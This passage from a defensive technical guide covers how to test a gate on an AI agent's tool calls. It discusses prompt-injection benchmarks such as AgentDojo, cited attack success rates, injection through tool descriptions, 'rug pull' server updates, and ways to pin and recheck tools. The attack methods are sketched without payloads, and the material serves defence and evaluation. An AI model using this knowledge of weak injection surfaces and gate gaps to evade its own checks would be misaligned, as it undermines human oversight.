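These percentages show what share of alarms are real, but not how often a gate would interrupt ordinary work. To measure that, the department could replay a month of real invoice jobs and count how many jobs still finish and how many harmless calls the gate stops or asks about. *CT0* (2026) reports that one guard model cut successful attacks from 16 to 4 of 64, but also cut completed ordinary tasks from 23 to 13 of 32. With a second guard, two attacks succeeded and the agent completed 22 tasks, so most of that loss was avoidable.

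### What a test without failures shows

If each trial fails with probability p, independently of the others, the chance of no failures in n trials is (1 − p)ⁿ. The upper 95% bound is the value of p at which that chance falls to 5%:

```
(1 − p)^n = 0.05
p = 1 − 0.05^(1/n)  ≈  3/n
```

TACIT, for example, leaked no secrets in 131 trials with each model, which gives a bound of about 2.3%.

| Trials, all without failure | Upper 95% bound on the failure rate |
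|---|---|
| 6 | 39% |
| 20 | 14% |
| 54 | 5.4% |
| 131 | 2.3% |
| 1,000 | 0.3% |
| 3,000 | 0.1% |

A rate of 2.3% is still high for a system under attack. At that rate, an attacker who made 100 independent attempts would have about a 90% chance of succeeding at least once.

The true uncertainty is often larger than the formula's result. Most of the 131 trials reused the same 10 injections. If the outcome depends mainly on the injection, the effective sample size is closer to 10 than to 131, and the bound for 10 trials is 26%. The formula also applies only if future attacks resemble the tested ones, but an attacker will look for one that doesn't.

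### Proofs and tests of the implementation

A proof about a type system covers every program that the formal rules accept, including programs written to defeat them, so running more tests wouldn't strengthen it. But the proof applies to a mathematical description of the language, so a mistake in the real compiler or library could break the guarantee even if the proof is correct.

Testing the implementation can reveal such mistakes. For each rule, a tester can write one program that breaks it and a nearly identical one that doesn't, much like the six small programs used to test ETAS. The tester can also generate thousands of random programs and check whether the compiler accepts and rejects them as the formal rules require. Finally, the tester can run accepted programs under a monitor. If a program has an effect that its type doesn't include, there is a mistake in the compiler or the library.

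Running trials with a language model is an inefficient way to find compiler bugs, because the model rarely writes the unusual programs that would expose them.

### What AgentDojo measures

AgentDojo tests whether an agent can finish ordinary tasks without obeying instructions planted in the data it reads. According to *SecOPD* (2026), version 1.2.1 has 949 pairs of user and attacker tasks, 560 of them in the office setting. The benchmark measures how many user tasks the agent completes with and without attacks, and how many attacks succeed.

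*Render Before Reading* (2026) explains that an attack counts as a success only if the agent achieves the attacker's goal with the required arguments. *Bounded Agents* (2026) points out that an injected call can therefore run without counting as a success, for example because the agent hadn't yet read the data it was supposed to steal. A gate fails whenever it lets a forbidden call run, so a tester should count those calls too.

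Attack success rates against undefended models vary widely. In *Kairos* (2026), attackers succeeded in 47.0% of cases on average with GPT-4.1, and in 28.3% and 32.3% with two other agents. *AutoDojo* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026) measured only 0.3% for Claude Haiku 4.5 with the benchmark's standard attack. Part of that resistance may be reluctance to act, since *Render Before Reading* reports that this model often put off unclear payments. None of these models is among the strongest of late 2026. In a different test, cited in *Bounded Agents*, attackers succeeded against all 13 frontier models, at rates from 0.5% to 8.5%.

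The results also depend on where the attacker's text appears. AgentDojo normally puts it in a tool's output. In *The Surface You Test Is Not the Surface That Breaks*, Sakib, Haque and colleagues (2026) moved the same text to a tool's description. The attack success rate rose from 8.8% to 74.6% for Gemini 3 Flash and fell from 54.9% to 6.8% for GPT-4.1. Across the 13 models, the relative ranking reversed in 35 of the 78 pairs.

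Ma and colleagues tested ten defences. Several filters stopped nearly all of the standard attacks but did much worse against attacks adapted to them. Defences that restrict the agent's actions or track information flow generally held up better. CaMeL was the most effective overall, but on four of the five models it also reduced success on ordinary tasks more than any other defence.

A high score can also come from training on similar cases. In *CorrGRPO* (2026), training a small model on AgentDojo cases raised its completion rate on ordinary tasks from 28.6% to 95.2%. The test used only 21 tasks, none of which were in the training data.

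AgentDojo can't show whether a gate classifies effects correctly. Claude Haiku 4.5 resists 99.7% of the standard attacks without a gate, so a gate that allowed every call would get the same score, as would a classifier that listed the payment tool as read-only. The benchmark's simulated tools also have no hidden network writes to find, no shell commands to analyse and no updates.

AgentDojo also doesn't measure every kind of leak. It tests whether an attacker diverted the agent. Odersky and colleagues wanted to know whether any secret reached the agent's output, so they wrote their own tests for TACIT.

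### When the tools change

A classification applies to one version of a tool, but some installations change versions without the user's approval. *A First Look at the Security Issues in the Model Context Protocol* (Li and Gao, 2025) notes that `npx`, a common command for starting servers, downloads the newest version each time if the user has chosen the `latest` tag. Hosts then load the new tool descriptions without checking them. *MCP-38* (2026) describes the attack this allows, a "rug pull", in which a server becomes harmful after users have come to trust it.

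Kraishan found that 40.6% of 8,900 servers with several published versions had changed their description or destination at least once while keeping the same identifiers. Most of these servers had only rewritten a description, but 370 had moved to a different host. Most changes are probably innocent, but users cannot tell from the registry whether a move was routine or a takeover.

Bharti (2026), in *Registry Descriptions Go Stale Unevenly*, followed the whole registry for 89 days and found that 11.9% of entries changed within 30 days. Rechecking the 5% of servers that had changed most often would catch only about a fifth of the known servers whose descriptions changed next. Bharti instead recommends rechecking an entry whenever its hash (a short fingerprint of its contents) changes, and regularly going through the whole registry.

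Registry entries don't contain tool definitions, so a gate has to track those itself:

1. Pin the exact version of each server and its dependencies, and store their hashes.
2. Store a hash of each tool's name, description, schema and annotations. If it changes, treat the tool as unclassified until someone has reviewed it.
3. Repeat the analysis at every update and compare the effect sets. A new effect, or a known effect that has become uncertain, goes to a person.
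4. Repeat the planted-fault tests when the analyser or its list of library functions changes.

Pinning a tool's version does not guarantee that its behavior stays the same. In *ProbeID*, Chen, Zhang and colleagues (2026) repeatedly called 59 tools over eleven weeks, and seven began to give different responses although their version numbers had not changed. This can happen when a pinned program relies on a remote service that changes.

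When the department approves a tool, ProbeID records the tool's responses to test inputs. It later repeats a secret selection of those inputs and compares the responses. This can reveal a change in an opaque service such as `lookup_vat`, but not a hidden effect that leaves the responses unchanged. Remote attestation could show that the program itself had changed, if the service's operator supported it.

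The record for each tool should also say what each entry rests on and when to check it again. *MCP Pitfall Lab* (2026) keeps a similar record for tool servers, which can include links to the test runs behind it. For the accounts department, some entries might be:

| Entry | Basis | Check again when |
|---|---|---|
| `write_file` has no network effects | proved, if the analysis covered all the code | the code, a dependency or the analyser changes |
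| `write_file` started no other programs in tests | observed | the code or the environment changes |
| `lookup_vat` does not store queries | declared by its operator | the terms change, and at regular intervals |
| Only staff can edit the supplier list | assumed | someone can verify the access settings |

A payment that relies on the supplier list is therefore only as safe as the assumption in the last row.

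### Symptoms and likely causes

| Symptom | Likely cause |
|---|---|
| A test run shows an effect that is missing from the record | a function chosen at run time, an unlisted library function or a changed tool |
| Many tools appear to have no effects | the analyser doesn't support the language or missed the entry points |
| Every tool on a server has the same long list of effects | the analyser didn't separate the branches of a shared dispatcher |
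| The same code gets different classifications | a language model does part of the analysis, or a dependency isn't pinned |
| Almost every call late in a conversation needs approval | label creep |
| No call ever fails a label check | unlabelled data counts as trusted, or labels get lost in files or memory |
| The classifier catches every planted fault but misses real ones | the faults are too simple, or the tester planted them after the step that selects tools |
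| Attacks fail even with the gate switched off | the model resists them, so the test says little about the gate |
| A tool's answers change but its version doesn't | a remote service or an unpinned dependency has changed |
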